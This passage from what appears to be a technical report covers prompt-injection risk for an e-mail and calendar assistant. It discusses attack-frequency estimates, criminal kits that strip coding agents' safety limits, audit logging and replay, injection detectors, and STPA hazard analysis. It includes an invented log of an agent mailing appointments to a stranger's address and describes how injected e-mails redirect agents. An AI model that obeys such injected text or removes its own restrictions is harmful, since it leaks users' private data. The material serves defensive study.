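Suppose 1,000 users each receive 100 messages a day, or 36.5 million a year in total, and s is 0.5%. If one message in a million is hostile, the developer should expect a leaked calendar about once every five and a half years. If one in 10,000 is hostile, she should expect about 18 leaks a year. Requiring approval for new recipients might seem a nuisance in the first case but would be clearly worthwhile in the second.

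Nobody has a reliable estimate of how often agents that read mailboxes are attacked. A successful attack can look like a harmless run, so the user may never notice it. Companies also rarely publish how many runs their agents complete, so outsiders who learn of ten incidents can't tell whether they came from a thousand runs or a billion.

### OWASP's vote and its incident records

Besides its list for agents, OWASP publishes a Top 10 for applications that contain a language model. Earlier editions relied on practitioners' votes, but for the August 2026 edition OWASP (2026) also analysed recorded incidents. According to the security company ReversingLabs, the project collected 7,714 records from public vulnerability databases and a database of AI harms, then built classifiers to read them; 6,639 records had enough detail to sort. ReversingLabs also reports that the vote carried three quarters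 of the weight and the incidents one quarter, because the project's leaders didn't want a single noisy year of data to outweigh the practitioners' votes.

The vote and the incidents disagreed most about prompt injection and misinformation:

| Risk | Rank in 2025 | Rank in 2026 | Vote and incidents compared |
|---|---:|---:|---|
| Prompt injection | 1 | 1 | First in the vote, outside the top ten by incidents |
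| Sensitive information disclosure | 2 | 2 | Close agreement |
| Excessive agency | 6 | 3 | Both supported the rise |
| Unbounded consumption | 10 | 6 | Practitioners' concern about costs drove the rise |
| Misinformation | 9 | 7 | Near the bottom of the vote, near the top by incidents |

OWASP attributes the gap for prompt injection to a "defense effect". Teams work hard to block such attacks, so fewer clean examples reach a public database and "the public count understates the risk" (quoted in Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents*). Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), a blog post from a company that sells security testing, goes further and concludes that low counts mean the defences are working.

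That conclusion needs evidence of many blocked attempts, which the incident records can't provide. It is also hard to reconcile with the experiments in which adaptive attackers broke most published defences. Steve Wilson, the project's founder, told ReversingLabs that prompt injection is as unavoidable as death and taxes, and that attackers' techniques are improving faster than models learn to detect them. If he is right, the main reason for the low count must be a lack of determined attackers or many unrecorded successes, rather than good defences.

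The records are also a poor measure of attack frequency because an entry in a vulnerability database usually describes a flaw rather than an attack. EchoLeak has one entry although Microsoft knew of no exploitation against customers, and a flaw that criminals used against a thousand companies could also have one entry. The counts also depend on how incidents are classified. In the calendar leak, prompt injection was the cause, excessive agency made it possible, and the result was disclosure of sensitive information. If the leak were classified only by its result, the count of prompt injection incidents would be one lower.

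Misinformation has the opposite pattern, and here the incidents deserve more attention than the vote. Even without an attacker, an assistant can misread Priya's message and move the meeting to the wrong day. Such errors may cost a company more than hostile e-mails do.

The list is also limited as a guide to agents. Help Net Security's *OWASP 2026 LLM Top 10* (2026) quotes the leaders as saying that once a model has tools, memory and downstream consequences, its risks belong in the separate agentic list. The people behind the ranking also have commercial interests. Wilson is an executive at Exabeam, a security company, and the sponsors that OWASP announced in September include firms that sell protection for agents.

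### Injected text on the web and in live traffic

Researchers can count hostile texts on public web pages whether or not any agent obeyed them. In April 2026 Google published a search of Common Crawl, a web archive with monthly snapshots of 2 to 3 billion pages. Its researchers first searched for familiar phrases, such as orders to ignore earlier instructions. They then used Google's Gemini model to classify each suspicious text by its purpose and by whether it belonged in the surrounding document, and people checked the results. These later steps were needed because most of the initial matches came from research papers, blog posts and security articles about prompt injection.

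Many of the remaining texts were pranks, such as an invisible request that AI assistants change their tone. Some site owners wanted assistants to add context to summaries or recommend their business. Others wanted to keep agents away, and one lured them to a page that never finished loading. Google found only a small number of attempts to steal data, and the example it gave was a site owner's experiment. Other pages contained commands to delete files on a user's computer, but Google considered the example it gave unlikely to work.

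The security companies Forcepoint and Check Point have published their own figures. Forcepoint searched public websites for attacks using alerts triggered by familiar phrases, according to Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild*. Check Point Research's *AI Security Report 2026* (2026) cites ten verified cases from that work and a larger scan by other researchers, and adds data from Check Point's own products.

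| Measurement | Denominator | Result | Serious attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Google | 2–3 billion pages per snapshot | Malicious texts rose 32% from November 2025 to February 2026 | Few attempts at data theft, but no published count |
| Scan cited by Check Point Research | 1.2 billion URLs | About 15,300 injected texts, or one per 78,000 URLs | Motives ranged from sabotage to marketing, with no breakdown |
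| Forcepoint | None | Ten verified cases | The cases aimed at fraud, data destruction or theft of access keys |
| Check Point Research | Prompts its products observed | Detections of long malicious texts rose about fivefold from March to May 2026, to nearly 1% | Unknown, because a detection isn't a confirmed attack |

All of these figures except the scan's come from companies with products to sell or defend. Google's 32% increase is hard to interpret without a page count, since it could mean a rise from 50 pages to 66 or from 5,000 to 6,600.

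Check Point's figure needs the most careful interpretation. A detector that raises a false alarm on 1% of harmless texts, like the invented one in the earlier example, would flag about 1% of texts even if nobody attacked. The increase is less informative because the traffic also changed. Check Point Research says that prompts came to include large blocks of web pages, documents and tool output as companies adopted agents, and a longer text gives a detector more chances to find something suspicious. Detections in short texts stayed about level.

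Check Point's researchers wrote cautiously that the pattern "suggests that indirect prompt injection is becoming more operationally relevant". In a heading on its marketing page, *The data and trends shaping the 2026 AI threat landscape*, the company described the same pattern as a fivefold rise in indirect prompt injections in three months. The data support a rise in detections of long texts, which may or may not reflect a rise in indirect prompt injections.

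None of these measurements gives h for the assistant. Text injected into a web page can reach any agent that visits the page, whereas the stranger chooses whom to e-mail. Even for a browsing agent, a rate of one injected text per 78,000 URLs doesn't mean that each visit has a 1 in 78,000 chance of encountering one, because agents don't visit URLs at random.

### Tools that criminals are building

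In April, Google saw little sign that attackers were using published data-theft techniques on a large scale. *Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Underhill, 2026) reports that by August criminals were developing indirect prompt injection tools to target agents. An attacker who buys such a tool needs less skill, but the tools' existence doesn't show how many people use them.

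Some reports of criminal tools describe attackers altering their own agents rather than attacking someone else's. Check Point Research found kits for sale on criminal forums that exploit a file a coding agent loads at the start of every session. The buyer puts the file in his own agent to remove its safety restrictions, then uses that agent to help him attack ordinary computers. Because agents trust project files, a victim who opens a project containing a malicious one can also be harmed, so a defender should ask whose agent a kit is meant to control.

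Criminals have also started to attack the software that connects agents to tools. GlassWorm, a self-spreading program, copied itself into MCP packages across more than 150 code repositories. It is ordinary malware that a company can look for with standard supply-chain checks.

Marketers may automate prompt injection before thieves do. Google found one elaborate text designed to make assistants promote a business. An automated search-optimisation program had apparently generated it. An agent that chooses suppliers or books travel could already encounter such texts in ordinary work.

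### Two explanations for the low counts

Attackers may have had easier routes than prompt injection. Someone who has stolen the assistant user's password, for example, can open her calendar without manipulating the model. Google argues that attackers weigh effort against benefit, and that prompt injection used to be difficult and compromised AI systems often failed to carry out the harmful action. Check Point Research describes many alternatives. One campaign stole logins for AI services and other credentials from more than 30,000 exposed configuration files, and the monitoring company GreyNoise recorded about 91,000 attack sessions against language-model deployments in a single quarter. The sessions are only attempts, but they show that attackers are interested in AI systems and often target the conventional software around the model.

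The other possibility is that successful attacks go unnoticed or are recorded under another cause. The companies that kept quiet after paying Guan, and the database that filed EchoLeak under command injection, show how this can happen. Similarly, in most of the cases Check Point Research documented of criminals using AI in intrusions, the attackers' own mistakes or the AI provider's monitoring, rather than the victim's defences, revealed the AI's role. New reporting rules may not help much. *The hardest AI security problems now live in what an agent is permitted to do* (Constantin, 2026) describes a European reporting duty that took effect on 11 September as "aimed elsewhere".

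Web scans are a partial test, because they count attempts whether or not victims notice them. If many serious attacks were succeeding unnoticed, the scans should find many serious attempts. Google found few, which supports the first explanation for public websites up to February 2026.

The support is weaker than it looks because Google's search began with well-known phrases and would miss text that avoided them. EchoLeak's e-mail read like instructions to an employee, and a similar web page could have escaped the search. Because the search finds clumsy attacks more easily than careful ones, it can make attackers seem less skilled than they are. Common Crawl also leaves out most social media and pages behind a login, and it contains no private mail, so the second explanation remains largely untested for e-mail assistants.

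### What an organisation can infer and measure

Public evidence shows that people plant hostile text for agents to find, so an organisation shouldn't set h to zero. It also shouldn't copy a rate from a vendor's report. It can instead try a low and a high value, as in the example at the start, and see whether its decision changes. A control that takes little effort, such as requiring approval for new recipients, may be justified against leaked appointments even at the low value. The organisation can wait for better data before deciding what to do about moved meetings.

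It can also collect that data itself. It should count the runs its agents complete and the items they read, separately for mail from known senders, mail from strangers, invitations and web pages. It should have people check a random sample of the detector's alarms, because false alarms inflate the estimate of h, and a sample of the texts that raised none, because missed attacks reduce it.

Reviewers can check completed runs for hijacking if the logs connect each action to what the agent had read. If they examine n randomly chosen runs and find none hijacked, they can be 95% confident that the true rate is below about 3/n. Finding no hijacking in 3,000 runs would still be consistent with a rate of one in 1,000, and ruling out a rate of one in 100,000 would take about 300,000 runs with no hijacking. Reviewers will learn more from the same effort by focusing on runs in which the agent read a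 stranger's text and then contacted someone new.

These estimates assume that reviewers recognise the attacks they see. To test that, the organisation can send harmless test injections to its own mailboxes without telling the reviewers. If they catch 60 of 100 tests and find 12 real attacks, the true number of attacks is probably nearer 20, or higher if real attackers hide their injections better than the testers.

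A decoy can reveal some leaks that nobody noticed. The developer could add a fake appointment to a test calendar, with a web address in its notes that appears nowhere else. If anyone outside the company visits that address, the notes have leaked, even if the outgoing message looked ordinary. The developer would still have to find out which run leaked them and why.

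## Auditing what an agent did and why

The developer must rely on what the harness recorded at the time to find out which run of the e-mail and calendar assistant leaked the appointments, and why. Auditors of ordinary software can infer what a program did from its code and input, but the assistant's code shows only that a loop ran and that the model could call four tools. The assistant might also act differently if she ran it again.

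### Why the log of a successful attack looks normal

The mail and calendar services probably keep their own logs. For the run in which a stranger's e-mail misled the assistant, the entries might be:

```
09:14:03  read_email     user's credential   success
09:14:09  list_events    user's credential   success
09:14:15  send_email     user's credential   success
09:14:21  update_event   user's credential   success
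09:14:26  send_email     user's credential   success
```

The user's credential permitted every call, and every call succeeded. The log would look the same if she had asked the assistant to send the week's plans to her travel agent before moving the meeting. Adding the recipient's address would help only an auditor who knew which addresses belonged to people she dealt with. The explanation for the third line is in the text the model had read by then, but the log doesn't include that text.

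David C advises developers to log enough to identify suspicious activity, which could include the model's full input and output, its tool calls and its API calls. He also recommends watching for failed calls, because an attacker will probably have to refine an attack before it works. If the assistant's harness required approval for new recipients, the developer could spot an attack from several rejected messages to the same unknown address before any appointments leaked.

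Many logging tools for agents still omit information an auditor would need. Wang, Sun and colleagues (2026) reviewed 90 studies in *Log Analysis for LLM-Based Agents* and found that logs commonly include inputs, outputs and timings, but less often include the model's reasoning or the permissions that allowed an action. A harness can observe inputs and outputs directly, but a developer has to write extra code to link a permission to the call it allowed.

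Shah and Kathrotia (2026), in *Securing and Auditing Long-Horizon LLM Agents*, measured how gaps in an agent's records affect the ability to trace faults. They created 240 synthetic runs and planted a fault in half of them, such as an instruction hidden in a tool result or an old approval that the agent reused. A program then tried to identify the exact step where each fault began. It succeeded in 10.8% of the faulty runs with records in the style of OpenTelemetry, a common standard for tracing software, in 16.7% with a log of tool calls, and in 98.3% with records of everything that passed between the context, memory, tools and other agents.

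The researchers chose both the faults and the fields that would reveal them, so the 98.3% result doesn't predict performance in real incidents. Their tests with some fields removed are more informative. Without the links between each passage and its source, the program found the right step in only 48.3% of faulty runs.

### What a record must hold

The harness should write a record for every step, including steps that appear harmless at the time:

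| Item | Question it answers |
|---|---|
| Full context, or its hash and a stored copy | What text did the model have when it chose this call? |
| Source of each passage | Who could have written that text? |
| Model and harness versions | Which software would an auditor have to run again? |
| Sampling settings | How much might another run differ by chance? |
| Tool descriptions as the model received them | Had a supplier changed a description since the user approved it? |
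| Proposed call and executed call | Did the harness change or block what the model asked for? |
| Policy decisions | Which rule allowed the call, and was a rule missing? |
| Approvals | What did the user agree to, and how often did the harness use that approval? |

A hash is a short value computed from a text, and any change to the text almost certainly changes the hash. A hash can therefore confirm that a stored copy matches the original, but nobody can recover the text from the hash if the copy is lost.

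For the third line of the log above, the assistant's record might look like this, with invented values and shortened hashes:

```
run and step      4471, step 3, 09:14:15 UTC
previous record   hash 9c1e...
acting for        user 208, request 1
versions          model build 2026-09-14, harness 2.3.1
sampling          temperature 0.7, seed not available
tool descriptions hash 77b0..., copy stored
context           hash 5f0a..., copy in restricted store
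  passage 1       developer's instructions
  passage 2       user's request to move Thursday's meeting
  passage 3       e-mail from Priya, from read_email in step 1
  passage 4       e-mail from unknown sender, from read_email in step 1
  passage 5       next week's events, from list_events in step 2
proposed call     send_email(to=plans@example.net, subject="Next week", body=...)
argument sources  to: exact match in passage 4
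                  body: matches nine events in passage 5
policy decision   format valid; no rule on recipients; allowed
approval          none required, none given
executed call     same as proposed; mail service accepted it
```

The entry for the recipient's address leads the auditor to the stranger's e-mail, and the policy entry identifies the missing control. The record of the proposed call would have been useful even if the harness had blocked the call, because it shows that something had misled the model. *Agentao* (Jin, Jiao and Tong, 2026) describes a harness that separates the model's proposals from the calls that the host program authorises. The harness does not formally guarantee safety, but it keeps evidence of both.

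The harness has to label each passage with its source when a tool returns it, and it can't rely on the passage's own text to do so, because a stranger could write in an e-mail that the user had supplied the text. Shah and Kathrotia cite an experiment in which one planted line made a simple source check miss most of the runs it would otherwise have flagged. Matching each tool result to the call that produced it fixed this weakness.

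Records also need to cover changes to the context. When a conversation becomes too long, many harnesses replace older parts with a summary. In one test that Shah and Kathrotia cite, such summaries kept on average only 17% of the user's constraints. Suppose the user told the assistant to write only to Priya, and a summary dropped that instruction. If the assistant then wrote to someone else as a result, an auditor with only the later context might blame a hostile e-mail instead of the missing instruction.

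Such records take up little space, not counting the stored text. In Shah and Kathrotia's test they averaged 524 bytes, or about half a megabyte per thousand records. A harness that, like Codex, resends the whole history at every step can store each passage once and list which passages each context contained.

### Tracing a value to its source

An auditor can turn these records into a provenance graph, which links each argument of a call to the text it came from. For the leaked calendar, part of the graph would be:

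```
stranger's e-mail  →  recipient  →  send_email
calendar entries   →  body       →  send_email
```

Ordinary code can trace a copied address by searching earlier passages for it, but a message body in which the model paraphrased the appointments would be harder to trace. The graph also doesn't show why the model made the call at all, since text can influence that choice without any of its words appearing in the arguments.

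The source of an action can also depend on what the auditor wants to know. *Auditing Agent Actions through Query-Conditioned Attribution* (Liu, Venkateswaran and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an agent that cancels a flight. The airline's policy and the customer's confirmation explain why it cancelled, while the customer's first message explains which booking number it used. The researchers wrote 1,396 questions of this kind about saved runs and tested automated ways to answer them. Their own system, which combines small open models with a larger one for disputed cases, found the right source for 64.5% of questions, compared with 60.4% for the best of the leading models used alone.

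Models can also give a correct answer that the evidence doesn't support. In *Correct Answers, Unsupported Findings*, Yun, Kim and colleagues (2026) had two models investigate saved runs of agents in a simulated bank. The agents had cited their inputs by labels such as "in-3". In 28 cases, an investigator needed a table matching labels to records to tell which record an agent had cited. Without the table, Claude Sonnet 4.6 still named a source in 26 of these cases and guessed correctly in 22. With the table, it gave a supported answer in 24 cases.

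A short program that looked up the labels answered every case correctly and returned no answer when the table was missing. A developer should therefore keep the table with the log and use ordinary code for lookups, even if a model writes the final report.

### Removing a message and replaying the run

An auditor can test whether a passage influenced an action by removing the passage and running the agent again. *CausalArmor* (2026) uses a version of this called leave-one-out, which measures how removing one span of text changes the model's likely output. With a complete record, an auditor can apply a similar test to whole runs.

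She restores the context as it was just after read_email returned, and connects the model to imitation tools so that nothing leaves the mailbox again. She then replays the run 20 times with the stranger's message and 20 times without it. Suppose she gets these invented results:

| | Appointments sent | Not sent | 95% interval for the rate |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| With the message | 14 | 6 | 48% to 85% |
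| Without the message | 0 | 20 | 0% to 16% |

If the message made no difference, the 14 leaks should be spread over both groups. The chance that all 14 would fall among the replays with the message is

C(20,14) / C(40,14) ≈ 1 in 600,000

where C(n,k) is the number of ways to choose k items from n. Chance is therefore a very poor explanation. The result is strong evidence that, with this model and the rest of this context, the message made the leak much more likely. The actual rates are less certain, as the wide intervals show.

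The auditor can't tell from the replays which sentence in the message mattered, whether its author meant harm, or whether the user had authorised the action. If the auditor removed Priya's message instead, the assistant would probably stop sending its confirmation, because it would no longer know the new time. Priya's message caused that confirmation legitimately. To tell the two cases apart, the auditor has to compare each call with what the user asked for.

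A negative result can mislead too. If two hostile messages contained the same instruction, removing only one might not change the leak rate, so the auditor should also try removing both. She could replace a message with a harmless one of similar length to check that the effect doesn't come from the shorter context.

Replays can also help identify the step at which the run went wrong. In *Causal Agent Replay*, Shah (2026) keeps everything before a chosen step fixed and has the model choose that step and all later ones again. Shah looks for the latest step at which choosing again still significantly changes the outcome. Suppose 14 of 20 replays leaked when the model chose again from its call to list_events, but all 20 leaked when it chose again from send_email. The assistant was then effectively committed to the leak once it had read the whole week's calendar, one call before the leak happened.

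This rule is necessary because changing an early step also gives every later step another chance to go differently, so an irrelevant first call could appear to matter. Shah's method found the right step in artificial models whose causes Shah had planted, which is a useful check but much easier than explaining what an agent did in a real mailbox. Shah notes that on a benchmark of failed runs by groups of agents, the best automated attempts to identify the responsible step from the record were right only about 14% of the time.

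### Why the same input can give different outputs

The auditor needs repeated replays partly because agents usually sample from several likely continuations. Setting the temperature to zero removes this sampling, since the software always takes the token with the highest score. The output may still vary because computers round numbers, so the order of an addition can change its result. In standard double-precision arithmetic, (0.1 + 0.2) + 0.3 gives 0.6000000000000001, while 0.1 + (0.2 + 0.3) gives 0.6. If two tokens have nearly equal scores, a difference that small can change which one scores higher, and the rest of the text then follows from a different token.

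*The Token Not Taken* (2026) explains why the order of additions changes. A server usually batches requests from several customers, and the batch size can affect how it groups the additions. Willison (2025), in *11th September 2025*, quotes a finding by the AI company Thinking Machines Lab that varying load is the main reason nearly all hosted models give inconsistent answers. Two auditors could therefore submit the same context and get different tool calls because other customers were busier during one of the tests.

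Running requests one at a time doesn't fully prevent the same request from producing different results. *Same Request, Different Answer* (2026) examines servers that reuse earlier calculations for the beginning of a prompt. Reuse changes how many tokens the server processes in one pass, which can change the result even when no other request is running.

Newer serving software can make outputs repeatable. *CoRun* (2026) reports a test in which 32 prompts on each of three models produced exactly the same tokens when run alone and in a batch of 32. The outputs were at most eight tokens long, much shorter than an agent's run. *Vosti* (2026) argues that the arithmetic, the scheduling of requests and the reuse of earlier calculations must all be deterministic, because a fault in any of them can change the answer.

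Making a model's answers repeatable can slow a server down. In a test of one common method, *LLM-42* (2026) found that a server's output fell by 56% when one of 11 simultaneous requests needed a deterministic answer. A company might therefore use the deterministic mode only for audits. Its replays would then match one another, but not necessarily the original run, which used the ordinary mode.

If the original run was also deterministic, an exact replay would be a good test of the record, because a missing passage or a changed tool description would often produce a different output. It wouldn't replace the 40 replays, because one run with the message and one without it might differ because of a trivial change in the text. The auditor would still need to repeat both with different random seeds. Users of hosted models often can't get exact replays. For them, Shah's tool reports how often the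 replay chose the same action as the original.

### Whether to believe the model's explanation

Asking the assistant why it sent the appointments would be much easier, but its answer is also generated text that the stranger's message may influence. Attackers in the Gray Swan competition similarly made agents hide what they had done.

Yun and colleagues asked agents, before each action, to briefly describe what they were about to do and list the inputs they had relied on. In one set of 54 runs containing an attack, four led to an unauthorised action that the researchers could trace to an earlier input. All four involved GPT-5.4 mini and the same bill-paying task. Each time, the list for the first unauthorised action left out the input that contained the attack, although in two of the runs the agent had cited it earlier. An auditor who trusted those lists would have investigated the wrong documents,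 but four cases are too few to show how often this happens.

Yun and colleagues point out that even an accurate citation records only what the agent named as its source, not whether that source caused the action. When a log contains no reasoning, some tools reconstruct the model's probable reasoning from its inputs and outputs. Wang and colleagues distinguish these reconstructions from reasoning the agent itself produced, and an auditor should keep the two separate in her report.

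An agent's explanations are still worth recording because auditors can use them to choose what to test. If the agent writes that it is sending the week's plans "as requested", an auditor can search the context for that request and replay the run without the passage that contains it.

### Detecting misdirection from provenance

A company with thousands of runs a day can't replay them all, so it needs a way to pick out suspicious ones. Sequeira and Iqbal designed Agent-Sentry to block such actions as they happen, by comparing them with an agent's earlier legitimate runs. It builds a provenance graph for each run and can check an action in three stages:

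1. A classifier examines the order of the calls and the origin of their arguments, without interpreting the text itself.
2. If the classifier is unsure, an allowlist accepts values such as recipients if they appeared in earlier legitimate runs and came from a trusted source this time.
3. A language model compares any remaining action with the user's request.

In a test on 5,380 recorded runs of seven agents, including 2,081 successful attacks, Agent-Sentry allowed 96.4% of legitimate runs and blocked 96.8% of attacks. Only 3.1% of decisions reached the language model. On tasks from two existing benchmarks that it hadn't trained on, it blocked 90.9% of attacks but allowed only 64.4% of legitimate runs. In many of those tasks, the agent must do something like pay the bill described in a file, so the legitimate account number also comes from untrusted text.

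If 1 run in 10,000 were hostile, nearly all the alarms would be false, as with any detector of rare attacks. But at the better of the two rates, an auditor could review about 360 runs instead of 10,000 and probably still find the hostile one.

Agent-Sentry also relies partly on the model to report where each argument came from. The software checks some of these reports, for instance by searching the named source for the value. Sequeira and Iqbal acknowledge that this reduces the problem but doesn't remove it. They also expect their system to miss a fake invoice that differs from a real one only in its account number. Its block rate hardly changed across three ways of wording the attacks, but the attacks in the test did not adapt to the defence.

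Other systems test what influenced an agent's actions while it is running. *AttriGuard* (2026) checks whether the user's task supports a tool call or whether untrusted content led the agent to go beyond what the task justified. It tests what caused the call because an attacker can easily make a bad call look plausible.

Ahad, Hossain and colleagues (2026) show in *Influence Is Not Authority* that knowing what caused an agent's action isn't enough to tell whether the user authorised it. They built 24 cases in which a user authorises an action, such as paying Alice. In one version the user supplies Alice's account number, and in the other the agent looks it up with a legitimate tool. The payment is identical, but a score modelled on CausalArmor's moved towards "attack" in all 24 cases when the number came from the tool. On average, this harmless change moved the score further than replacing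 Alice with an unauthorised recipient did.

AttriGuard had similar difficulty with these cases, blocking 47.1% of authorised actions and 36.3% of unauthorised ones, a difference that could be due to chance. It did better in a separate test with live agents, where it reduced unauthorised outcomes from 24.3% to 2.9% when outside text conflicted with the user's request. Measures of influence can therefore help stop attacks, but a high score doesn't prove that an attack occurred.

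### Protecting the log

Anyone who can alter the log can hide an attack, so the agent shouldn't have permission to edit it. A common further protection is a hash chain, in which each record's hash also covers the hash before it:

hash(n) = H(record n, hash(n − 1))

If someone changes record 3, its hash no longer matches the one stored in record 4. To hide the change, they would have to recompute every later hash. An operator who controls the whole log could do that, or delete the most recent records without breaking the chain. The developer can guard against both by regularly sending the latest hash to someone outside the company. Shah and Kathrotia describe a system that can post such hashes to a public ledger. Its chained logs add about 48 microseconds per event.

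An intact hash chain doesn't prove that the harness recorded everything. If the assistant can send data through an image address and the harness logs only tool calls, the chain will be intact but omit the leak. Shah and Kathrotia list unlogged routes and attackers who flood the log with events among the problems their design leaves open.

The full log is also a second copy of the user's mailbox, and may contain passwords or access tokens that passed through a tool call. Shah and Kathrotia recommend putting the full text in an encrypted or access-controlled store. The main log can then use keyed hashes for fixed identifiers. Without the key, anyone could hash a list of likely e-mail addresses and look for a match.

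Keeping the text separate also makes deletion easier. If Priya asks the company to erase her messages, it can delete them from the store and leave the chain of hashes intact. The auditor would still know that a message had been there, but could no longer replay the run with it.

The people and programs that read the log also need protection. The log includes the stranger's original instructions, so a model that summarises it for the auditor could follow them. That model should have no tools that can send data out.

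### Legal duties to keep records

Article 12 of the EU AI Act requires systems the Act classes as high-risk, such as those that screen job applicants, to be able to record events automatically throughout their lifetime. The logs must help people identify risks and monitor how the system works. Articles 19 and 26 require providers and deployers to keep the logs they control for at least six months, unless other law, particularly data-protection law, provides otherwise.

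These duties were due to apply from August 2026, but the EU has postponed them. According to *EU Digital Omnibus on AI Enters Into Force* (National Law Review, July 2026), they will now apply from 2 December 2027 to the high-risk uses that the Act lists, including recruitment, and from 2 August 2028 to AI in products already covered by EU safety law.

An assistant that only moves and confirms meetings would probably not count as high-risk, but it probably would if a company also used it to rank job applications arriving by e-mail. The Act describes what the logs are for but, except for remote biometric identification, doesn't list the fields they must contain. It is therefore unclear whether a bare list of tool calls would satisfy the Act, although such a list wouldn't be enough to explain the leaked calendar.

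Data-protection law applies to the assistant's logs whether or not the assistant is high-risk, because they contain personal data about the user and everyone who writes to her. Under the EU's General Data Protection Regulation, a company may keep such data in identifiable form only as long as the purpose of processing it requires, but an audit may need the data for longer. Shah and Kathrotia recommend keeping the source text for as long as anything derived from it remains in an agent's memory. For example, if the assistant copies a stranger's instruction into the notes of a yearly event, the developer may need a year-old record to explain what the assistant does when the event recurs.

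## Analysing failures in which no part broke

An investigator can use records and replays to find which message led the e-mail and calendar assistant to leak its user's appointments. She also has to explain why the leak was possible, so that the developer can prevent the next one. With older engineering methods, she would look for a part that failed, but every part of the assistant worked.

### What fault trees and failure tables assume

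In a failure modes and effects analysis (FMEA), an engineer lists each component of a system, how it could fail and what would follow. For the assistant, part of the table might be:

| Component | How it could fail | Effect | What it did when the calendar leaked |
|---|---|---|---|
| read_email | Returns nothing | The assistant misses Priya's proposal | Returned all the recent messages |
| Calendar service | Loses a change | The meeting stays on Thursday | Saved the change |
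| Harness | Runs a malformed call | A service reports an error | Ran only well-formed calls |
| send_email | Loses a message | Priya never hears about the new time | Delivered both messages |

An engineer could complete this table without finding the leak, because nothing in the second column happened.

A fault tree starts from the harm and works down to the failures that could cause it, joined by AND and OR. It has the same shape as an attack tree, but engineers usually give each failure a probability. If two independent failures must both occur, the probability of the harm is

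P(harm) = p₁ × p₂

Suppose the assistant had two filters, each missing 1% of hostile e-mails. The tree would put the chance of a hostile e-mail passing both at 0.01 × 0.01, or one in 10,000. Multiplying makes sense for two valves that wear out separately, but a stranger can reword a message until both filters miss it, then send that version to everyone.

The *STPA Handbook* (Leveson and Thomas, 2018) explains that these probabilities only make sense if failures are random, which failures of software and people are not. The older methods also assume that a component behaves the same way in the whole system as it does alone. The handbook describes several accidents in which it is hard to name a failed component. The Mars Polar Lander had to switch off its engines as soon as it landed, so its software monitored sensors in the legs. The sensors gave false signals when the legs unfolded. Engineers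 expected this, but the software's requirements didn't mention it, and the software switched off the engines 40 metres above the surface.

In a less serious case, a car-rental company in Washington state fitted its cars with an anti-theft device that disabled any car moving with its engine off. When customers took the cars on a ferry, the device worked as intended and disabled the cars, and the ferry service stopped until tow trucks had removed them.

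A presentation published by INCOSE, a society of systems engineers, uses the lander to distinguish safety from reliability. An assistant that often crashes before it does anything is unreliable but safe, while one that sends every message it is told to send is reliable but unsafe.

An engineer could add a row to the FMEA table for a model that follows a stranger's instructions. The row would be a useful reminder, but she couldn't give that failure a single probability, because adaptive attacks succeed far more often than fixed ones. The row also wouldn't cover harms that occur when the model follows only the user's instructions.

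### Hazards from functions that work as intended

Car makers have a similar problem with driver-assistance systems. For example, an emergency-braking system might brake hard for a shadow even though its camera, computer and brakes all work. ISO 26262 covers faults in a vehicle's electronics. A separate standard, ISO 21448 (ISO, 2022), covers hazards from "functional insufficiencies", which arise when the specification leaves something out or when the system performs too poorly for the situation.

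Both can occur in the assistant. Its specification has no rule about who may receive a message, and its model may perform poorly by confusing two contacts called Priya. The standard also covers reasonably foreseeable misuse, such as a user approving a message without reading it.

ISO 21448 excludes cybersecurity threats and deliberate actions that clearly violate a system's intended use. An agent's developer would find it hard to separate security from safety like this. A model's mistake and a hostile e-mail can lead to the same call to send_email, and one rule restricting recipients could block the call in both cases.

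### Applying STPA to the assistant

System-Theoretic Process Analysis (STPA) covers all these causes in one analysis. It attributes accidents to inadequate control over a system, whether or not a component has failed. *RL-STPA* (2026), which adapts the method to systems trained by reinforcement learning, divides STPA into five steps: define the losses and hazards, draw the control structure, identify unsafe control actions, work out why they might occur, and derive requirements that prevent them.

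The analyst first lists the losses, which are outcomes the people affected want to avoid. For the assistant, the losses include private information reaching the wrong person and someone missing a meeting.

*Exploring Systems-Thinking Approaches to Loss of Control Risk* (2026) defines a hazard as a system state that leads to a loss in worst-case conditions. One hazard for the assistant is that the calendar lists the meeting on Friday while Priya still expects it on Thursday. This may do no harm if she checks her calendar in time, but in the worst case she travels to a meeting that nobody else attends. The analyst can reverse a hazard to get a constraint, in this case that the calendar and the guests' information must agree.

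Next, she draws the control structure. A controller gives commands, called control actions, and receives feedback about their effects. The assistant has four controllers:

| Controller | What it controls | Control actions | Feedback |
|---|---|---|---|
| Developer | The model and the harness | Instructions, permissions and rules | Logs and complaints |
| User | The model | Requests | The assistant's replies |
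| Model | The calendar and outgoing mail | Proposed tool calls | Tool results |
| Harness | The model's access to the services | Running or blocking a call | Status messages from the services |

She then checks whether each controller gets the feedback it needs. Leveson and Thomas describe a flight simulator whose pedals kept breaking, although identical pedals lasted in real aircraft. A real aircraft's nose dips slightly when it stops, but the simulator didn't reproduce this, so pilots kept braking harder and longer than necessary. The solution is better feedback, since stronger pedals would treat only the symptom. The assistant's user also lacks feedback when the reply confirms that the meeting has moved but omits the message to the stranger.

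In this structure, prompt injection is a command sent through a feedback channel. The stranger puts the command in an e-mail, which the model receives as feedback about the mailbox.

Thomas (2019) gives four ways in which a control action can be unsafe. A controller may fail to give it, give it when it causes a hazard, give it at the wrong time or in the wrong order, or stop it too soon or continue it too long. For send_email, the analyst might write:

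| Type of unsafe action | Example | Constraint |
|---|---|---|
| Not given | The meeting moves, but the assistant doesn't tell Priya | Every guest must receive notice of a new time |
| Wrongly given | The assistant sends the week's appointments to a stranger | A message may contain only what its recipient is allowed to know |
| Wrong time or order | The assistant confirms Friday before it changes the calendar, and the change then fails | The harness sends a confirmation only after the calendar reports success |
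| Wrong duration | The assistant stops after telling two of five guests, or keeps sending reminders after all five have replied | Each guest receives one notice per change |

Sending one e-mail takes an instant, so the last row treats a series of messages as one action.

The analyst still has to ask why each unsafe action might occur. The assistant could send appointments to the wrong person because an attacker asked for them by e-mail, because the model confused two addresses, or because a summary of a long conversation left out the user's instruction to write only to Priya. The constraint on what a recipient may know covers every cause, including any the analyst didn't think of.

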